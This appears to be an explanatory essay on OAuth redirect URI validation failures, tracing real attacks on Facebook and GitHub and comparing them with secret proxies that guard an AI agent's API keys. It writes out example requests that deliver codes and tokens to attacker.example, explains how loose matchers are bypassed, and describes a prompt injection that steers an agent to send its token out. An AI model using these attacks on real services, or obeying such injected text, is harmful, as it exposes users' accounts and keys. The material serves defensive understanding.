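# OAuth redirect URI validation failures and what they teach about binding secrets to destinations

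## How OAuth delivers a credential, and how a secret proxy does

OAuth is a protocol that lets a person give one application limited access to their account at another service without sharing their password. The Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which publishes many internet standards, issued version 2.0 in October 2012. Most people have used OAuth through a "Sign in with" button. OAuth itself only grants access, so these buttons usually run on OpenID Connect, a layer on top of OAuth that also gives the application the user's identity.

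In the common form of OAuth, the service delivers a credential by sending the user's browser to a web address, the redirect URI, with the credential attached. Whoever controls that address gets the credential, so the service checks the requested address against those the application has registered. For more than a decade, many services checked loosely, and attackers stole credentials as a result.

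AI agents need keys to call web services. One way to supply them is a secret proxy, a program that sits between the agent and the network and adds the real key to permitted outgoing requests. People who run agents this way now face a problem similar to OAuth's, because the proxy has to determine which addresses may receive which key.

### The parties and the registered address

Before OAuth, a printing service that wanted a customer's pictures from a photo-sharing site had to ask for the customer's password and keep a copy. The password gave the service access to the whole account, and the customer could revoke that access only by changing the password, which also shut out every other application that used it. *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework* (Hardt, 2012), the text of the standard, uses this example and defines four roles. The customer is the resource owner. The printing service is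 the client, which here can mean a whole website with its own servers. The machine that stores the photos is the resource server. The authorization server logs the customer in, asks for approval and issues credentials. One company often runs both servers, and many studies, including *OAuth 2.0 Redirect URI Validation Falls Short, Literally* (Innocenti, Golinelli and colleagues, 2023), call the combination an identity provider.

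The client needs an access token, a string that the resource server accepts as evidence of permission. A token allows a limited range of actions for a limited time. Most are bearer tokens, which anyone who holds them can use.

Before any of this can happen, the client's developers register it with the authorization server, typically through a web form. They supply one or more redirect URIs and receive a public client identifier. A client that runs on its own server usually also gets a client secret, which works like a password. Hardt calls such clients confidential. Phone apps and code that runs in the browser are public clients, because anyone can extract a password shipped inside them. The 2012 standard requires public clients to register their redirect URIs and recommends that other clients do so too. Hardt notes that a correct redirect URI does not prove who sent a request, since anyone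 can copy it, but it can keep the server from delivering the credential to an impostor.

Developers mostly notice the rule when they break it. In a Google forum thread, *Getting error redirect_uri_mismatch when using oAuth*, a reply quotes Google's documentation, which says the redirect URI in the request must exactly match a registered one, including case and trailing slash.

### The authorization code grant

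In OAuth, a grant is a way of obtaining a token. In the authorization code grant, the browser carries a short-lived code, which the client exchanges for the token.

Suppose the printing service lives at print.example and the photo site's authorization server at login.photos.example. The customer clicks "Import my photos", and the printing service redirects the browser to the authorization server with this request (the names and values are invented, and the line breaks are only for reading):

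```
GET /authorize?response_type=code
    &client_id=print-shop-41
    &state=k7Qz
    &redirect_uri=https%3A%2F%2Fprint.example%2Fcallback
Host: login.photos.example
```

The first parameter specifies that the reply should contain a code, and `client_id` identifies the printing service. The client checks the reply for the `state` value so that it can reject replies it didn't request. `redirect_uri` is the address for the reply, with %3A and %2F encoding a colon and a slash.

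The authorization server looks up the client and compares the redirect URI with the registered ones. If none matches, it must not send the browser there, and should show the user an error instead. If one matches, it logs the customer in and asks whether the printing service may see the photos. After a yes, it answers the browser:

```
HTTP/1.1 302 Found
Location: https://print.example/callback?code=Xw93bTqL&state=k7Qz
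```

Status 302 makes the browser go to the address on the second line, which delivers the code to the printing service. The code itself does not give access to the photo account, so the printing service's server contacts the authorization server directly, sends the code with its client secret, and receives an access token. It presents that token to the resource server and gets the photos.

OAuth sends the customer's browser to the authorization server so that the customer types the photo-site password only there. The browser then returns to the printing service with a code, which lets the service know that the person using it is the one who approved the request. However, credentials can leak from a browser. Lodderstedt (2013), in *OAuth 2.0 Security*, an early analysis of threats to the protocol, points out that addresses end up in browser caches and log files, and that browsers pass them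 to other sites in the Referer header, which names the page a visitor came from. Lodderstedt gives two reasons for using a code. It is short-lived, so a leak does less harm than a leaked token would, and the authorization server can authenticate a client far more easily over a direct connection than through a user's browser. Hardt also limits a code to one use and says it should last at most ten minutes. If a code arrives a second time, the server must refuse it and should revoke any tokens it has already issued for it.

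The weak point is the authorization request, which reaches the authorization server as an ordinary link in the user's browser. In the basic protocol, nothing in the request is secret or signed, so an attacker can write the same link with `redirect_uri` pointing to attacker.example. *Best Current Practice for OAuth 2.0 Security* (Lodderstedt, Bradley and colleagues), the IETF's current security advice, tells implementers to assume that an attacker can steer a user's browser to any address at any time, for instance with a malicious ad or a plausible email. It also assumes that this attacker cannot read traffic meant for someone else, so the redirect URI determines who can read the code. A user who opens the altered link sees the photo site's real login page, which asks about a printing service the user may already trust. If the server approves repeat requests automatically, the user isn't asked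 at all.

### The check at the code exchange

*Redirect URL Validation*, a guide for people who build OAuth services, lists three times to validate the redirect URL: when a developer registers it, when an authorization request arrives, and when the client exchanges the code. The last check is easy to overlook because the server has already sent the code by then.

It exists because a stolen code is useful even to an attacker who lacks the client secret. With a public client the attacker can simply take the code to the authorization server and collect a token. With a confidential client the attacker has to make the client do it, and Hardt describes how:

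1. The attacker opens an ordinary account at the printing service, starts to import photos, and copies the authorization link that the service produces.
2. The attacker changes the redirect URI in the link to an address of their own and tricks the victim into opening it.
3. The victim sees a normal approval page and agrees. If the authorization server accepts the altered address, the code goes to the attacker.
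4. The attacker visits the printing service's genuine callback address with the victim's code.
5. The printing service exchanges the code, using its own valid secret, and links the victim's photos to the attacker's account.

To stop this, Hardt requires a client that included a redirect URI in its authorization request to repeat it when exchanging the code. The authorization server must confirm that the two are identical. In the attack, the printing service sends its own callback address, but the server issued the code for a request that named the attacker's address, so it refuses the exchange.

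The check works only if the server remembers which address it used for each code. Comparing the repeated address with the registered list is no substitute, because the printing service's genuine address is on that list and will pass. Lodderstedt and colleagues report that some providers do exactly this, and that providers "very often ignore" the check altogether, perhaps because the standard does not make its purpose obvious. The repair came from elsewhere. Hardt, Parecki and Lodderstedt (2026), in *The OAuth 2.1 Authorization Framework*, a draft successor to the 2012 standard, drop the redirect URI from the exchange and rely on PKCE, by which a client proves that it began the request that produced the code. (The draft's own walk-through of the grant still includes the old parameter.)

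### The implicit grant

The 2012 standard also defines a shorter route, the implicit grant, for applications that run entirely in the browser. The client asks for `response_type=token`, and the authorization server puts the access token itself in the redirect URI, after a # sign: `https://print.example/callback#access_token=...`. Browsers don't send this part of the address, the fragment, when they request a page, so the token does not reach the web server directly. A script on the returned page reads it instead. This saves a round trip but removes the exchange, and with it the checks on the client secret and the repeated redirect URI. The remaining protection is the comparison with the registered address. If that comparison wrongly accepts an attacker's address, the attacker's page immediately receives a working token. Lodderstedt and colleagues advise clients against the implicit grant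 unless they have closed off these leaks, and the 2.1 draft omits it.

### What a secret proxy does

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses the actions, such as running a command or calling a web service. The easy way to let an agent use a service is to put the key in the agent's environment, where the agent can read and leak it. A secret proxy instead gives the agent a placeholder and replaces it with the real key only after the request has left the agent.

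*Credential proxy*, part of the documentation for fnox, a tool that supplies secrets to other programs, gives an example. The user writes a rule that allows a GitHub token to be sent to api.github.com in the Authorization header (the line of a web request that carries credentials), for requests that read, create or change things under one group of code repositories. The user then starts a coding agent through the proxy. The agent finds a placeholder called GITHUB_TOKEN in its environment and uses it as if it were the real token. The proxy compares each request's domain, method, path and header with the rule. If all of them match, it replaces the placeholder with the token and sends the request on.

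Encryption would normally prevent the proxy from reading or editing that header. fnox therefore creates a temporary certificate authority, which issues certificates that confirm a site's identity, and configures the agent's software to trust it. The proxy can then decrypt the request, edit it, and encrypt it again for the real server, whose certificate it verifies. If a reply contains the token, the proxy replaces it with the placeholder before the agent receives it.

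The proxy cannot treat a request's destination as the user's choice. In a prompt injection, an attacker hides instructions in material the agent will read, such as a web page, an email or a comment in a code repository, and the agent follows them as if they came from its user. Those instructions can tell the agent to send a request, including credentials, to an address the attacker chose.

Suppose a poisoned web page gets the agent to send its GitHub token to attacker.example. Under fnox's default setting, the proxy blocks the request because no rule mentions that host. Under the looser setting, the proxy forwards traffic without a rule unchanged, so the attacker receives only the worthless placeholder. To get the real token through the proxy, an attacker has to find a request that satisfies a rule and still delivers the token somewhere it should not go. An attacker could also bypass the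 proxy. The fnox documentation warns that a process running under the same user account can ignore the proxy or ask fnox for the secret directly, and it advises running untrusted agents in a container or virtual machine with the proxy as the only network route out.

### The structure both share

Both arrangements are forms of destination binding, a rule that a secret may go only to listed destinations. The parts line up as follows.

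| Part | OAuth | Secret proxy |
|---|---|---|
| Secret | Authorization code, or the access token in the implicit grant | API key or token |
| Party that releases it | Authorization server | Proxy |
| Requested destination | `redirect_uri` in the authorization request | Address of the agent's outgoing request |
| Attacker's influence | A doctored link that the user opens | Injected text that the agent reads |
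| Registered set | The client's registered redirect URIs | The user's rules for that secret |
| Comparison | Before the redirect | Before the swap |

Let *R*(*s*) be the set of destinations registered for a secret *s*, and let *d* be the requested destination. The releasing party sends *s* to *d* only if match(*d*, *r*) is true for some *r* in *R*(*s*). Most of the difficulty is in defining the match function. Under exact matching, it is true only when *d* and *r* are identical character for character. Looser matching lets one registered entry cover many addresses, and an attacker needs only one that the function accepts but the developer did not intend. Even a perfect match function does not control what happens to the secret after it arrives.

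The analogy between OAuth and secret proxies still has to be tested. The OAuth rules cited here govern authorization servers, clients and resource servers, and at least four differences could keep them from applying to secret proxies.

OAuth's redirect step delivers a credential to the client, which will use it somewhere else, whereas a secret proxy sends the key to the service that accepts it. Lodderstedt and colleagues describe an OAuth attack that is a closer parallel to the proxy's situation: an attacker sets up a counterfeit resource server and gets a client to send it a token that is valid elsewhere. They tie the risk to clients that learn the server's address at runtime rather than having it built in. An agent that browses and calls services on request learns many of its addresses that way.

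An OAuth client needs only one or a few callback addresses and can register each in full. An agent that works with GitHub needs a different path for almost every request, too many to list in advance. fnox matches the domain exactly and the path by a pattern, so the strictest OAuth rule, which requires the whole address to match exactly, cannot carry over unchanged.

A wrong match may also do more harm with a proxy than with OAuth's code grant. The code grant releases a code that should expire within minutes and work only once. If the client is confidential, a thief who lacks the client secret cannot exchange the code directly and has to get the client to redeem it, as in the attack Hardt describes. A proxy releases the key itself, as the implicit grant releases the token, and API keys often stay valid for months.

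A secret proxy opens the connection to the destination itself, so it can verify the server's identity before sending the key. An OAuth authorization server can't do this because it only gives the browser an address and never contacts that address.

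## 2007 to 2013: registered addresses and loose comparison

OAuth 1.0, which a small group of web developers settled in October 2007, let a client name a different return address each time it sent a user to approve access, rather than using a registered one. *OAuth* (Hammer-Lahav and Cook, 2008), an early IETF draft of the protocol, describes the steps. The client first sends the server a signed request for a request token, a temporary value that identifies one attempt to get access. It then sends the user's browser to the server with the request token and, optionally, an `oauth_callback` parameter that holds the return address. Once the user approves, the server sends the browser to that address with the request token attached. In a final signed request, the client trades the approved request token for an access token.

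The client signed the requests it made directly, but not the link that passed through the browser, so anyone who got the link could change its callback. Hammer-Lahav and Cook do not ask the server to compare the callback with anything. Twitter's first version was stricter than the protocol. In *OAuth*, a post to Twitter's developer forum, Kristian (2007) reported as a bug that Twitter ignored the callback in the request and used the one registered for the client. Alex Payne of Twitter replied that the company knew its service did not yet follow the specification.

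### The session fixation attack of 2009

On April 20, 2009, Twitter took its OAuth support offline, and three days later the OAuth community published a security advisory. Both dates come from *Guess it’s time to wait for OAuth 1.1* (2009), a blog post by a developer who had raised a related worry on the mailing lists a few days before. According to the advisory text in CGISecurity's *OAuth Session Fixation Security Flaw Discovered* (2009), the attack goes like this:

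1. The attacker logs into their own account at an honest client and starts to connect it to the provider.
2. Instead of following the redirect, the attacker saves the authorization link, which contains the request token.
3. The attacker persuades a victim to open the link. The victim sees the provider's real approval page, with the name of an honest client on it, and approves.
4. The attacker uses the saved request token to finish the process, and can then reach the victim's data through the client.

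The victim has no way to notice the attack. Willison (2009) called the flaw a "show-stopper" and advised people not to start an OAuth flow from an untrusted location until there was a fix.

The caller-supplied callback made the attack easier. A careful client might have noticed that the wrong person had come back, but the attacker could change `oauth_callback` in the saved link so that the victim's browser never returned to the client. But a registered callback would not have been enough to prevent the attack. Eran Hammer-Lahav, who coordinated the response, considered a client that used the account of whoever came back, checked that the same user had started and finished, and had a callback fixed at registration. Even that client was open to a race, in which the attacker visits the callback after the victim approves but before the victim's browser arrives.

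The race worked because the callback carried only the request token. The attacker had held that token from the start, so controlling its destination did little good.

The community published a revised protocol, OAuth 1.0a, in June 2009. *The OAuth 1.0 Protocol* (Hammer-Lahav, 2010) documents two relevant changes. The client now sends the callback in its first, signed request, so someone who holds only the browser link cannot alter it. The server also creates an unguessable verification code after the user approves, sends it through the browser to the callback, and requires it before issuing an access token. The attacker who started the process never sees that code. Developers were slow to adopt the changes. In January 2010, Hedlund (2010) reported in *Confused about OAuth 1.0 vs 1.0a and Twitter API docs* checking the other available code examples and finding none that supported the verification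 code.

### The rules of 2012 and 2013

OAuth 2.0 has no signed first step, and the client again puts the redirect URI in the browser link, as it did in 2007. The authorization code replaces the verification code, and Hardt describes it as a way to check that the person who approved access is the person who came back. The code is secret, so it must go to the right destination, and the only safeguard at the first step is comparing the redirect URI with a registered address.

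Hardt requires public clients, and confidential clients that use the implicit grant, to register. A server should ask for the complete redirect URI. Anything that differs between requests can go in the `state` parameter, which the server returns unchanged. Where complete registration is not possible, the server should at least require the scheme, the host with any port, and the path, so that only the query (the part after the question mark) can vary. A client may register several addresses.

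When a client has registered a full address, Hardt requires the server to use "simple string comparison", a term from the general IETF standard for web addresses. Innocenti quotes the definition in *Look at the source*, a talk on OAuth security. The server compares the two strings one pair of characters at a time, in order, until the strings end or a pair differs. `https://print.example/cb` and `https://PRINT.example/cb` therefore do not match, even though a browser treats them as the same place. When the client has registered only part of an address, Hardt tells the server to match the registered "URI components" and points to the same standard, but gives no procedure. Later researchers disagreed about whether this text was clear enough.

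Even the fallback is fairly strict. If the printing service registers `https://print.example/cb` without a query, it may use `https://print.example/cb?album=7`, but no other host or page. Servers that accepted wildcard hosts or path prefixes were looser than Hardt recommends. The recommendation allowed this because it uses the word "should", which in IETF documents leaves room for exceptions. Hardt warns that partial registration lets an attacker pass the check with an open redirector on the client's site, a weakness that attackers exploited soon afterwards.

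The advice became firmer in January 2013, when *OAuth 2.0 Threat Model and Security Considerations* (Lodderstedt, 2013) recommended that every client register a full redirect URI. If a request names a different URI, the server should assume that an attacker sent the request, refuse it, and not redirect the browser. Alternatively, the server can ignore the URI in the request and always use the registered one, which is the behavior Kristian had reported to Twitter as a bug.

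Lodderstedt also recommends that a server skip the approval page for a returning user only if it has authenticated the client or validated a pre-registered redirect URI. If that validation is loose, the server also skips the page for an attacker's request, and the victim sees nothing.

The IETF published this document as informational rather than as a standard, so nobody had to follow it. Lodderstedt also concedes that registration might not scale. Developers often registered clients by hand, and no standard yet existed for automating this. A client that found its servers only at runtime might not be able to register in advance.

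### Why developers wanted patterns

Suppose the printing service has grown. It runs separate copies for development, testing and production, gives each business customer a subdomain such as `acme.print.example`, and wants to return people to the album they were viewing when they clicked "Import my photos".

With 200 customers and three environments, full registration takes 600 addresses, and every new customer adds three more. If the address also names the album, the list grows with every new album. A single pattern, `https://*.print.example/*`, covers all these addresses in one line of a form. Lodderstedt and colleagues give the same two reasons for using patterns, which are that a client can register once for many addresses and can carry transaction state in extra parameters.

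Loose comparison also came partly from habit. In OAuth 1.0 the callback could include the client's own query parameters, and the server had to keep them. After the 2009 attack, developers of Shindig, Apache software for running small applications inside social sites, expected many providers to require registered callbacks. They planned on the assumption that they could still vary the query, that varying the path "might be OK", and that they could not vary the host.

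A client could get the same results without patterns. All 200 customers could return to one address, say `https://login.print.example/cb`, with a random `state` value that the printing service looks up to find the right customer and album. This is more work for the client, which has to store the value and forward the user itself. The client would also become an open redirector if it forwarded users to any address it received. A pattern moves the work to the authorization server, but Lodderstedt and colleagues consider this a bad tradeoff because pattern matching proved harder to implement and easier to get wrong than exact matching. They report that attackers have exploited both faulty matchers and careless patterns.

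### How loose matchers go wrong

In the examples below, the developer's real callback is `https://app.print.example/callback`. Two facts about web addresses explain most of the errors. The host ends at the first slash after `https://`, so anything later is only a path. Control over a host name runs from right to left, so the owner of `attacker.example` can create any name that ends in `.attacker.example`.

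A server that accepts any address beginning with `https://app.print.example` does not check where the hostname ends. An attacker who controls `attacker.example` can use `https://app.print.example.attacker.example/callback`, which the server accepts because it begins with the registered string. Adding a slash to the end of the registered string fixes this error, because the attacker's address has a dot in that position.

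A server can make the opposite mistake by checking only the end of the host. If the host must end in `print.example`, `https://blueprint.example/callback` passes, and anyone could buy that domain. The suffix needs a leading dot, `.print.example`, plus a separate entry if the bare domain should work too.

Wildcards fail when they match more than their author intended. In `https://*.print.example/*`, the first star should match part of a host name. If the server lets it match any characters, including slashes, the server will accept `https://attacker.example/.print.example/cb`. Here the star matches `attacker.example/`, and the trusted name is part of the path.

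A wildcard that matches dots can be just as bad on shared hosting. Suppose a developer registers `https://print-*.hosting.example/cb` to cover test copies such as `print-17.hosting.example`. If the star matches dots, the pattern also matches `https://print-x.mallory.hosting.example/cb`, and a customer called mallory may control every name under `mallory.hosting.example`.

Matching by path prefix keeps the redirect on the registered host but lets an attacker choose a different page there. A server that accepts anything beginning with `https://app.print.example/callback` also accepts `/callback-help` and `https://app.print.example/callback/../forum/9`. In a path, `..` means "go up one level", so the browser resolves the second address and requests `/forum/9`. Labunets (2016), in *Lessons from breaking and defending OAuth 2.0 in practice*, gives the example of GitHub's documented rule, which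 required the host and port to match exactly and the path to be a subdirectory of the registered one. Labunets points out that `/../` can lead the server and the browser to interpret the same address differently. To steal the code, the attacker still needs the other page to leak it, for instance by forwarding the browser elsewhere.

The table shows how six matchers handle six addresses, of which only the first is the real callback. Each matcher reads the address as written, without resolving `..` first. "Loose wildcard" is `https://*.print.example/*`, where the stars match any characters. "Strict wildcard" is the same pattern, but the first star matches only a single part of a host name, with no dots or slashes.

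| Requested address | Exact | Path prefix | Host prefix, no boundary | Host suffix, no dot | Loose wildcard | Strict wildcard |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| `https://app.print.example/callback` | accept | accept | accept | accept | accept | accept |
| `https://app.print.example.attacker.example/callback` | refuse | refuse | accept | refuse | refuse | refuse |
| `https://blueprint.example/callback` | refuse | refuse | refuse | accept | refuse | refuse |
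| `https://attacker.example/.print.example/cb` | refuse | refuse | refuse | refuse | accept | refuse |
| `https://promo.print.example/callback` | refuse | refuse | refuse | accept | accept | accept |
| `https://app.print.example/callback/../forum/9` | refuse | accept | accept | accept | accept | accept |

No single test address would expose all the faulty matchers without also flagging the strict wildcard, which works as its author intended. Every matcher in the table gives the right answer for the real callback and for an address like `https://attacker.example/`, so a developer who tests only those two won't find the faults.

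Some servers did not compare the redirect URI with the registered address at all. Al Rahat, Feng and Tian (2022) found this flaw in ApiFest, an open-source server, using *Cerberus*, a tool that searches OAuth server code for logical flaws. ApiFest used the client's registered address only when the request omitted the redirect URI. If the request included one, the server sent the authorization code there without checking the registration.

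### The wildcard attack, request by request

Lodderstedt and colleagues give a worked example of a loose wildcard. A client registers `https://*.somesite.example/*` to allow addresses such as `https://app1.somesite.example/redirect`, but the authorization server treats the star as matching any character.

The attacker first gets the user to open a page under the attacker's control, `https://www.evil.example`. That page makes the browser send an authorization request in the client's name (the identifier, `state` value and code in these messages are invented):

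```
GET /authorize?client_id=album-app-7
    &redirect_uri=https%3A%2F%2Fattacker.example%2F.somesite.example
    &response_type=code
    &state=Jt5w
Host: server.somesite.example
```

The server decodes the redirect URI to `https://attacker.example/.somesite.example` and compares it with the pattern. (Taken literally, the pattern also needs a slash after `.somesite.example`, which this address lacks. A server that treats the final `/*` as optional accepts it as it stands, and for a server that doesn't, the attacker only has to add a slash.) The comparison succeeds, and once the user approves, the server answers:

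```
HTTP/1.1 302 Found
Location: https://attacker.example/.somesite.example?code=Rm42vKpe&state=Jt5w
```

The browser obeys and makes the third request of the attack, this time to the attacker's server:

```
GET /.somesite.example?code=Rm42vKpe&state=Jt5w
Host: attacker.example
```

The attacker reads the code from the web server's log. The `state` value does not prevent this, because the attacker wrote the request and the client never sees the reply.

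What the code is worth depends on the client. If the client is public, the attacker sends the code straight to the authorization server:

```
POST /token
Host: server.somesite.example

grant_type=authorization_code&code=Rm42vKpe
&client_id=album-app-7
&redirect_uri=https%3A%2F%2Fattacker.example%2F.somesite.example
```

Hardt's rule that the redirect URI must be the same at the exchange does not help here, because the attacker repeats the address from the first request. PKCE would not help either, because the attacker writes the authorization request and so chooses the value that the exchange must match. The attacker receives an access token and often a refresh token, a longer-lasting credential for getting new access tokens after the first expires.

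If the client is confidential, the attacker has to get the genuine client to redeem the code, as in the attack Hardt describes. Lodderstedt notes that an attacker with a stolen code can log in as the victim if the client uses OAuth for login. The exchange check does help here, if the server performs it properly, because the client sends its own callback address, not the attacker's.

### A correct wildcard and a lost subdomain

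The pattern `https://*.somesite.example/*` is unsafe even if the authorization server matches it correctly. The developer intended it to allow any page on any host inside `somesite.example`, so an attacker who gains control of one of those hosts can still collect authorization codes.

Lodderstedt and colleagues describe how an outdated DNS record makes this possible. DNS is the system that translates host names into network addresses, and one of its record types, the CNAME, makes one name an alias for another. Companies use it to put an outside service, such as a help desk or a shop, under their own domain. The attack takes four steps:

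1. The company signs up with an outside service as `customer-abc` and creates a CNAME record that points `external-service.somesite.example` to `customer-abc.service.example`.
2. Later the company cancels its account, and `customer-abc.service.example` disappears. Nobody deletes the CNAME record.
3. The attacker signs up with the same service and asks for the name `customer-abc`. Visitors to `external-service.somesite.example` now reach the attacker's account.
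4. The attacker sends users an authorization link with `https://external-service.somesite.example/` as the redirect URI. The server correctly finds that it matches the pattern, and sends the code.

HTTPS does not reveal that an attacker has taken over a host. Lodderstedt puts high confidence in a matching redirect URI when the client is a web application, because the browser checks the host's certificate before it sends anything. But a certificate confirms only that whoever runs the server controls that host name. After a takeover, the attacker controls it and can usually get a valid certificate.

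The pattern in effect allows codes to be sent to any host in the domain, including hosts that other teams set up for other purposes and hosts that did not exist when the developer filled in the form. The same problem arises without any DNS mistake if the company gives customers subdomains where they can run their own code, since a hostile customer then needs only an ordinary account to exploit it.

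The authorization server cannot detect the takeover by comparing strings, because the pattern was meant to allow the address. Only the company can clean up its DNS records, and the people who maintain them may not know that an OAuth registration depends on them. If the developer had registered `https://app1.somesite.example/redirect` in full, as the later exact-match rule requires, taking over `external-service` would not have helped the attacker at this step, though taking over `app1` itself would still have worked.

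## 2013 to 2014: stealing credentials through the permitted site

An attacker can sometimes steal a credential without exploiting a faulty comparison or a lost subdomain. In 2013 and 2014, researchers stole credentials that Facebook and GitHub had sent to genuine sites, on hosts the providers meant to allow. A page on each site leaked the credential.

Often that page was an open redirector, which forwards the browser to any address given in its parameters. Sites build them to count clicks on outgoing links, or to return people to what they were reading before they logged in. Few developers treated them as an urgent problem. Homakov (2013), in *The Achilles Heel of OAuth*, points out that OWASP, which publishes web security advice, warned only that open redirectors could help with phishing.

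### How a browser carries a token to another site

In the implicit grant, the access token travels in the URL fragment, which the browser does not send when it requests a page. But if the server responds with a redirect to an address that has no fragment, the browser attaches the old one, even when the new address is on a different site.

Lodderstedt and colleagues explain how an attacker can exploit this. A client registers `https://client.somesite.example/cb?*`, which fixes the host and path and lets only the parameters vary. This is as narrow as Hardt's fallback for partial registration. But the page at `/cb` is also an open redirector, which sends the browser to whatever address is in the `redirect_to` parameter.

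The attacker gets the user to open a page that starts this request (the values are invented, and the encoding is simpler than in the original):

```
GET /authorize?response_type=token
    &client_id=album-app-7
    &state=Jt5w
    &redirect_uri=https%3A%2F%2Fclient.somesite.example%2Fcb
     %3Fredirect_to%3Dhttps%253A%252F%252Fattacker.example%252F
Host: server.somesite.example
```

The attacker encodes their own address twice so that it is still a parameter value after the server decodes the request. The host and path match the pattern, so once the user approves, the server issues a token:

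```
HTTP/1.1 303 See Other
Location: https://client.somesite.example/cb
          ?redirect_to=https%3A%2F%2Fattacker.example%2F
          #access_token=Vn83kLsd&state=Jt5w
```

The browser requests `/cb` from the client and holds on to the fragment. The client reads `redirect_to` and answers:

```
HTTP/1.1 303 See Other
Location: https://attacker.example/
```

This address has no fragment, so the browser goes to `https://attacker.example/#access_token=Vn83kLsd&state=Jt5w`, where a script on the attacker's page reads the token. The authorization server applied the pattern correctly. The client's server could not have checked `state` before forwarding the browser, because it was in the fragment too. If the developer had registered `/cb` alone and the authorization server had required an exact match, it would have refused the first request.

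Authorization codes are harder to steal this way because they travel in the query, which the browser does not carry over to the next address. *Make Redirection Evil Again*, a later Black Hat talk, therefore lists two conditions for the attack. The provider must support the implicit grant, and the client must have an open redirector. The first condition is easier to meet than it sounds. Homakov complained that `response_type` is a parameter in the link, not a fixed client setting, so an attacker can request a token even if the client's developers only use codes.

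Poole (2011) had already used this behavior to steal a Facebook token. At the time, every Facebook application accepted a return address on facebook.com, and one page there, `login_status.php`, redirected visitors to the site of the application named in the link. Poole registered an application, had Facebook send another application's token to that page, and read the token when it arrived at a page Poole controlled. The attack worked in Firefox 5 and Chrome 13 but not in Internet Explorer 9. Lodderstedt and colleagues list this change in how browsers treat fragments among their reasons for updating OAuth's security advice.

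A server can block the carry-over by adding a meaningless fragment to its own redirects. Homakov explains that Facebook appends `#_=_` because an attacker could previously give Facebook's own login page, set up for the attacker's application, as the return address for someone else's application. Facebook then forwarded the browser to the attacker with the other application's token still attached. The added fragment protects only Facebook's redirects, so a client with a redirector has to add its own.

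### Facebook, February to April 2013

Security researcher Nir Goldshlager attacked Facebook's OAuth in three ways within about two months. The Hacker News (2013) described the first attack in February. The attack began with the return address in Facebook's approval link. Facebook's site could open another of its pages from text after a # sign, and Goldshlager found that `%23~!` (`%23` is an encoded #) worked in every browser. This could send a user to any file or folder on Facebook's domain. Goldshlager chose their own small Facebook application, which forwarded the browser to an outside server that logged the tokens.

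The victim did not have to approve anything, because Goldshlager put Facebook Messenger's identifier in the link. Messenger was a built-in application with automatic access to all accounts, according to Help Net Security's *OAuth flaw allowed researcher full access to any Facebook account*. Facebook fixed the flaw and told Business Insider (*A Developer Found A Hole In Facebook's Security*) that it had no evidence of anyone exploiting it and had paid a bounty of an undisclosed amount.

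Facebook's fix was a pattern that rejected return addresses with one encoded hash sign but still allowed two or more. In *How I Hacked Any Facebook Account...Again!*, which the developer site Aliyun reposted, Goldshlager describes getting past it:

1. An address with two hash signs also led to other pages, but only on Facebook's main site. The OAuth check rejected the main site and most subdomains, and accepted the mobile ones, where the trick failed. It also accepted `facebook.facebook.com`, where the trick worked.
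2. The token did not survive more than three redirects, so Goldshlager needed a short route to the malicious application. Facebook's script for outgoing links, `l.php`, offered one.
3. That script normally showed a warning first. Putting five extra bytes before the address suppressed the warning when the destination was another Facebook subdomain.
4. The application forwarded the browser to Goldshlager's server, which logged the token.

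The token carried Messenger's permissions, including reading the mailbox, and worked until the victim changed their password. Two-step verification did not stop the attack. Goldshlager reported this chain on March 6, and writes that Facebook fixed it immediately. The fixes dealt with particular tricks but left the return address flexible.

In April, Goldshlager used addresses on other companies' sites instead of Facebook's own pages. The Hacker News published two links that requested a token using the identifiers of the Skype and Dropbox applications. The return address in the Skype link was on `metrics.skype.com` and contained `REDIR/?url=` followed by the address of Goldshlager's server. The one in the Dropbox link was `www.dropbox.com/u/68182951/redirect3.html`, which looks like a file in one user's folder. Both hosts belonged to the companies that ran the applications, so the return addresses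 passed a check on the domain.

The Hacker News reported that Facebook could not fix this itself because application developers were responsible for their own sites. Botezatu (2013), in *Account Hijack with a Twist*, used the word "unfixable" in the headline. Facebook could not repair Skype's redirector, but it could have stopped sending tokens there. Three weeks earlier, Homakov had suggested that Facebook do this by recording the return addresses each application used most and allowing only those. This would have broken applications that varied their addresses. Facebook eventually built an exact-match setting, which its *Security Checklist* calls Strict Mode.

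Researchers kept finding flaws, and Facebook kept paying for them. Homakov joked that the bounty hunters were happy with things as they were, given "so much $$$ floating around redirect_uri". *A story of a $9500 bug in Facebook OAuth 2.0* (l33tdawg, 2013) reports that Andrey Labunets found several weaknesses in 2012 and 2013, many of which leaked access tokens. Labunets later co-wrote the IETF's advice.

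### How a page leaks a code

A page can also leak a code without redirecting the browser. When a browser loads an image from another server, it can send the current page's address in the Referer header. Browsers at the time normally sent the full address, including the query string and the code in it.

Suppose the printing service runs a forum where anyone can post images, and its authorization server matches by path prefix. The server accepts `https://app.print.example/callback/../forum/9`, which the browser opens as `/forum/9`. If an attacker has posted an image there from their own server, the browser sends that server this request:

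```
GET /pixel.png
Host: attacker.example
Referer: https://app.print.example/forum/9?code=Xw93bTqL&state=k7Qz
```

Lodderstedt and colleagues write that this can happen when the page loads outside content, as it did here, or when the user clicks a link on the page.

The choice of page matters because a code works only once. The real callback page usually exchanges the code right away, so an attacker can do little with a later leak. The forum page doesn't use it, so the code stays valid until it expires. Lodderstedt and colleagues advise clients to keep outside content off the page that receives the reply and to send a `Referrer-Policy: no-referrer` header, which stops the browser from including the page's address in the `Referer` header.

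The check at the code exchange is a second defense, because the printing service sends its real callback address, not the forum's. Homakov reports that the Russian social network VK did not make this check until September 2012, and that an image on a client's site could leak a usable code.

### GitHub, February 2014

GitHub started paying for security reports in early 2014, and Homakov looked at its OAuth service again. *How I hacked Github again* (Homakov, 2014) describes an attack that combined five bugs to gain access to a victim's private code. The attack targeted Gist, GitHub's service for sharing snippets of text and code. Gist is an OAuth client that GitHub had approved in advance, so users never saw an approval page.

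1. GitHub required the path of the redirect URI to be a subdirectory of the registered one, but it did not resolve `..` first. Homakov asked for `https://gist.github.com/auth/github/callback/../../../homakov/8820324`, and GitHub accepted it.
2. GitHub redirected the browser to that address with a code. The browser went up three levels and opened `gist.github.com/homakov/8820324?code=CODE`, a page that Homakov had written.
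3. The page contained an image. GitHub normally replaced image addresses with the address of its own proxy, which kept the Referer header from reaching other servers. Homakov wrote the address as `///attackersite.com`. GitHub's Ruby software read this as a path on its own site and left it alone, but Chrome and Firefox read it as another host and sent the code there.
4. Homakov took the code to Gist's real callback. GitHub should have refused the exchange because the redirect URI was different, but it issued a token whatever address the client sent. Homakov was now logged in to Gist as the victim.
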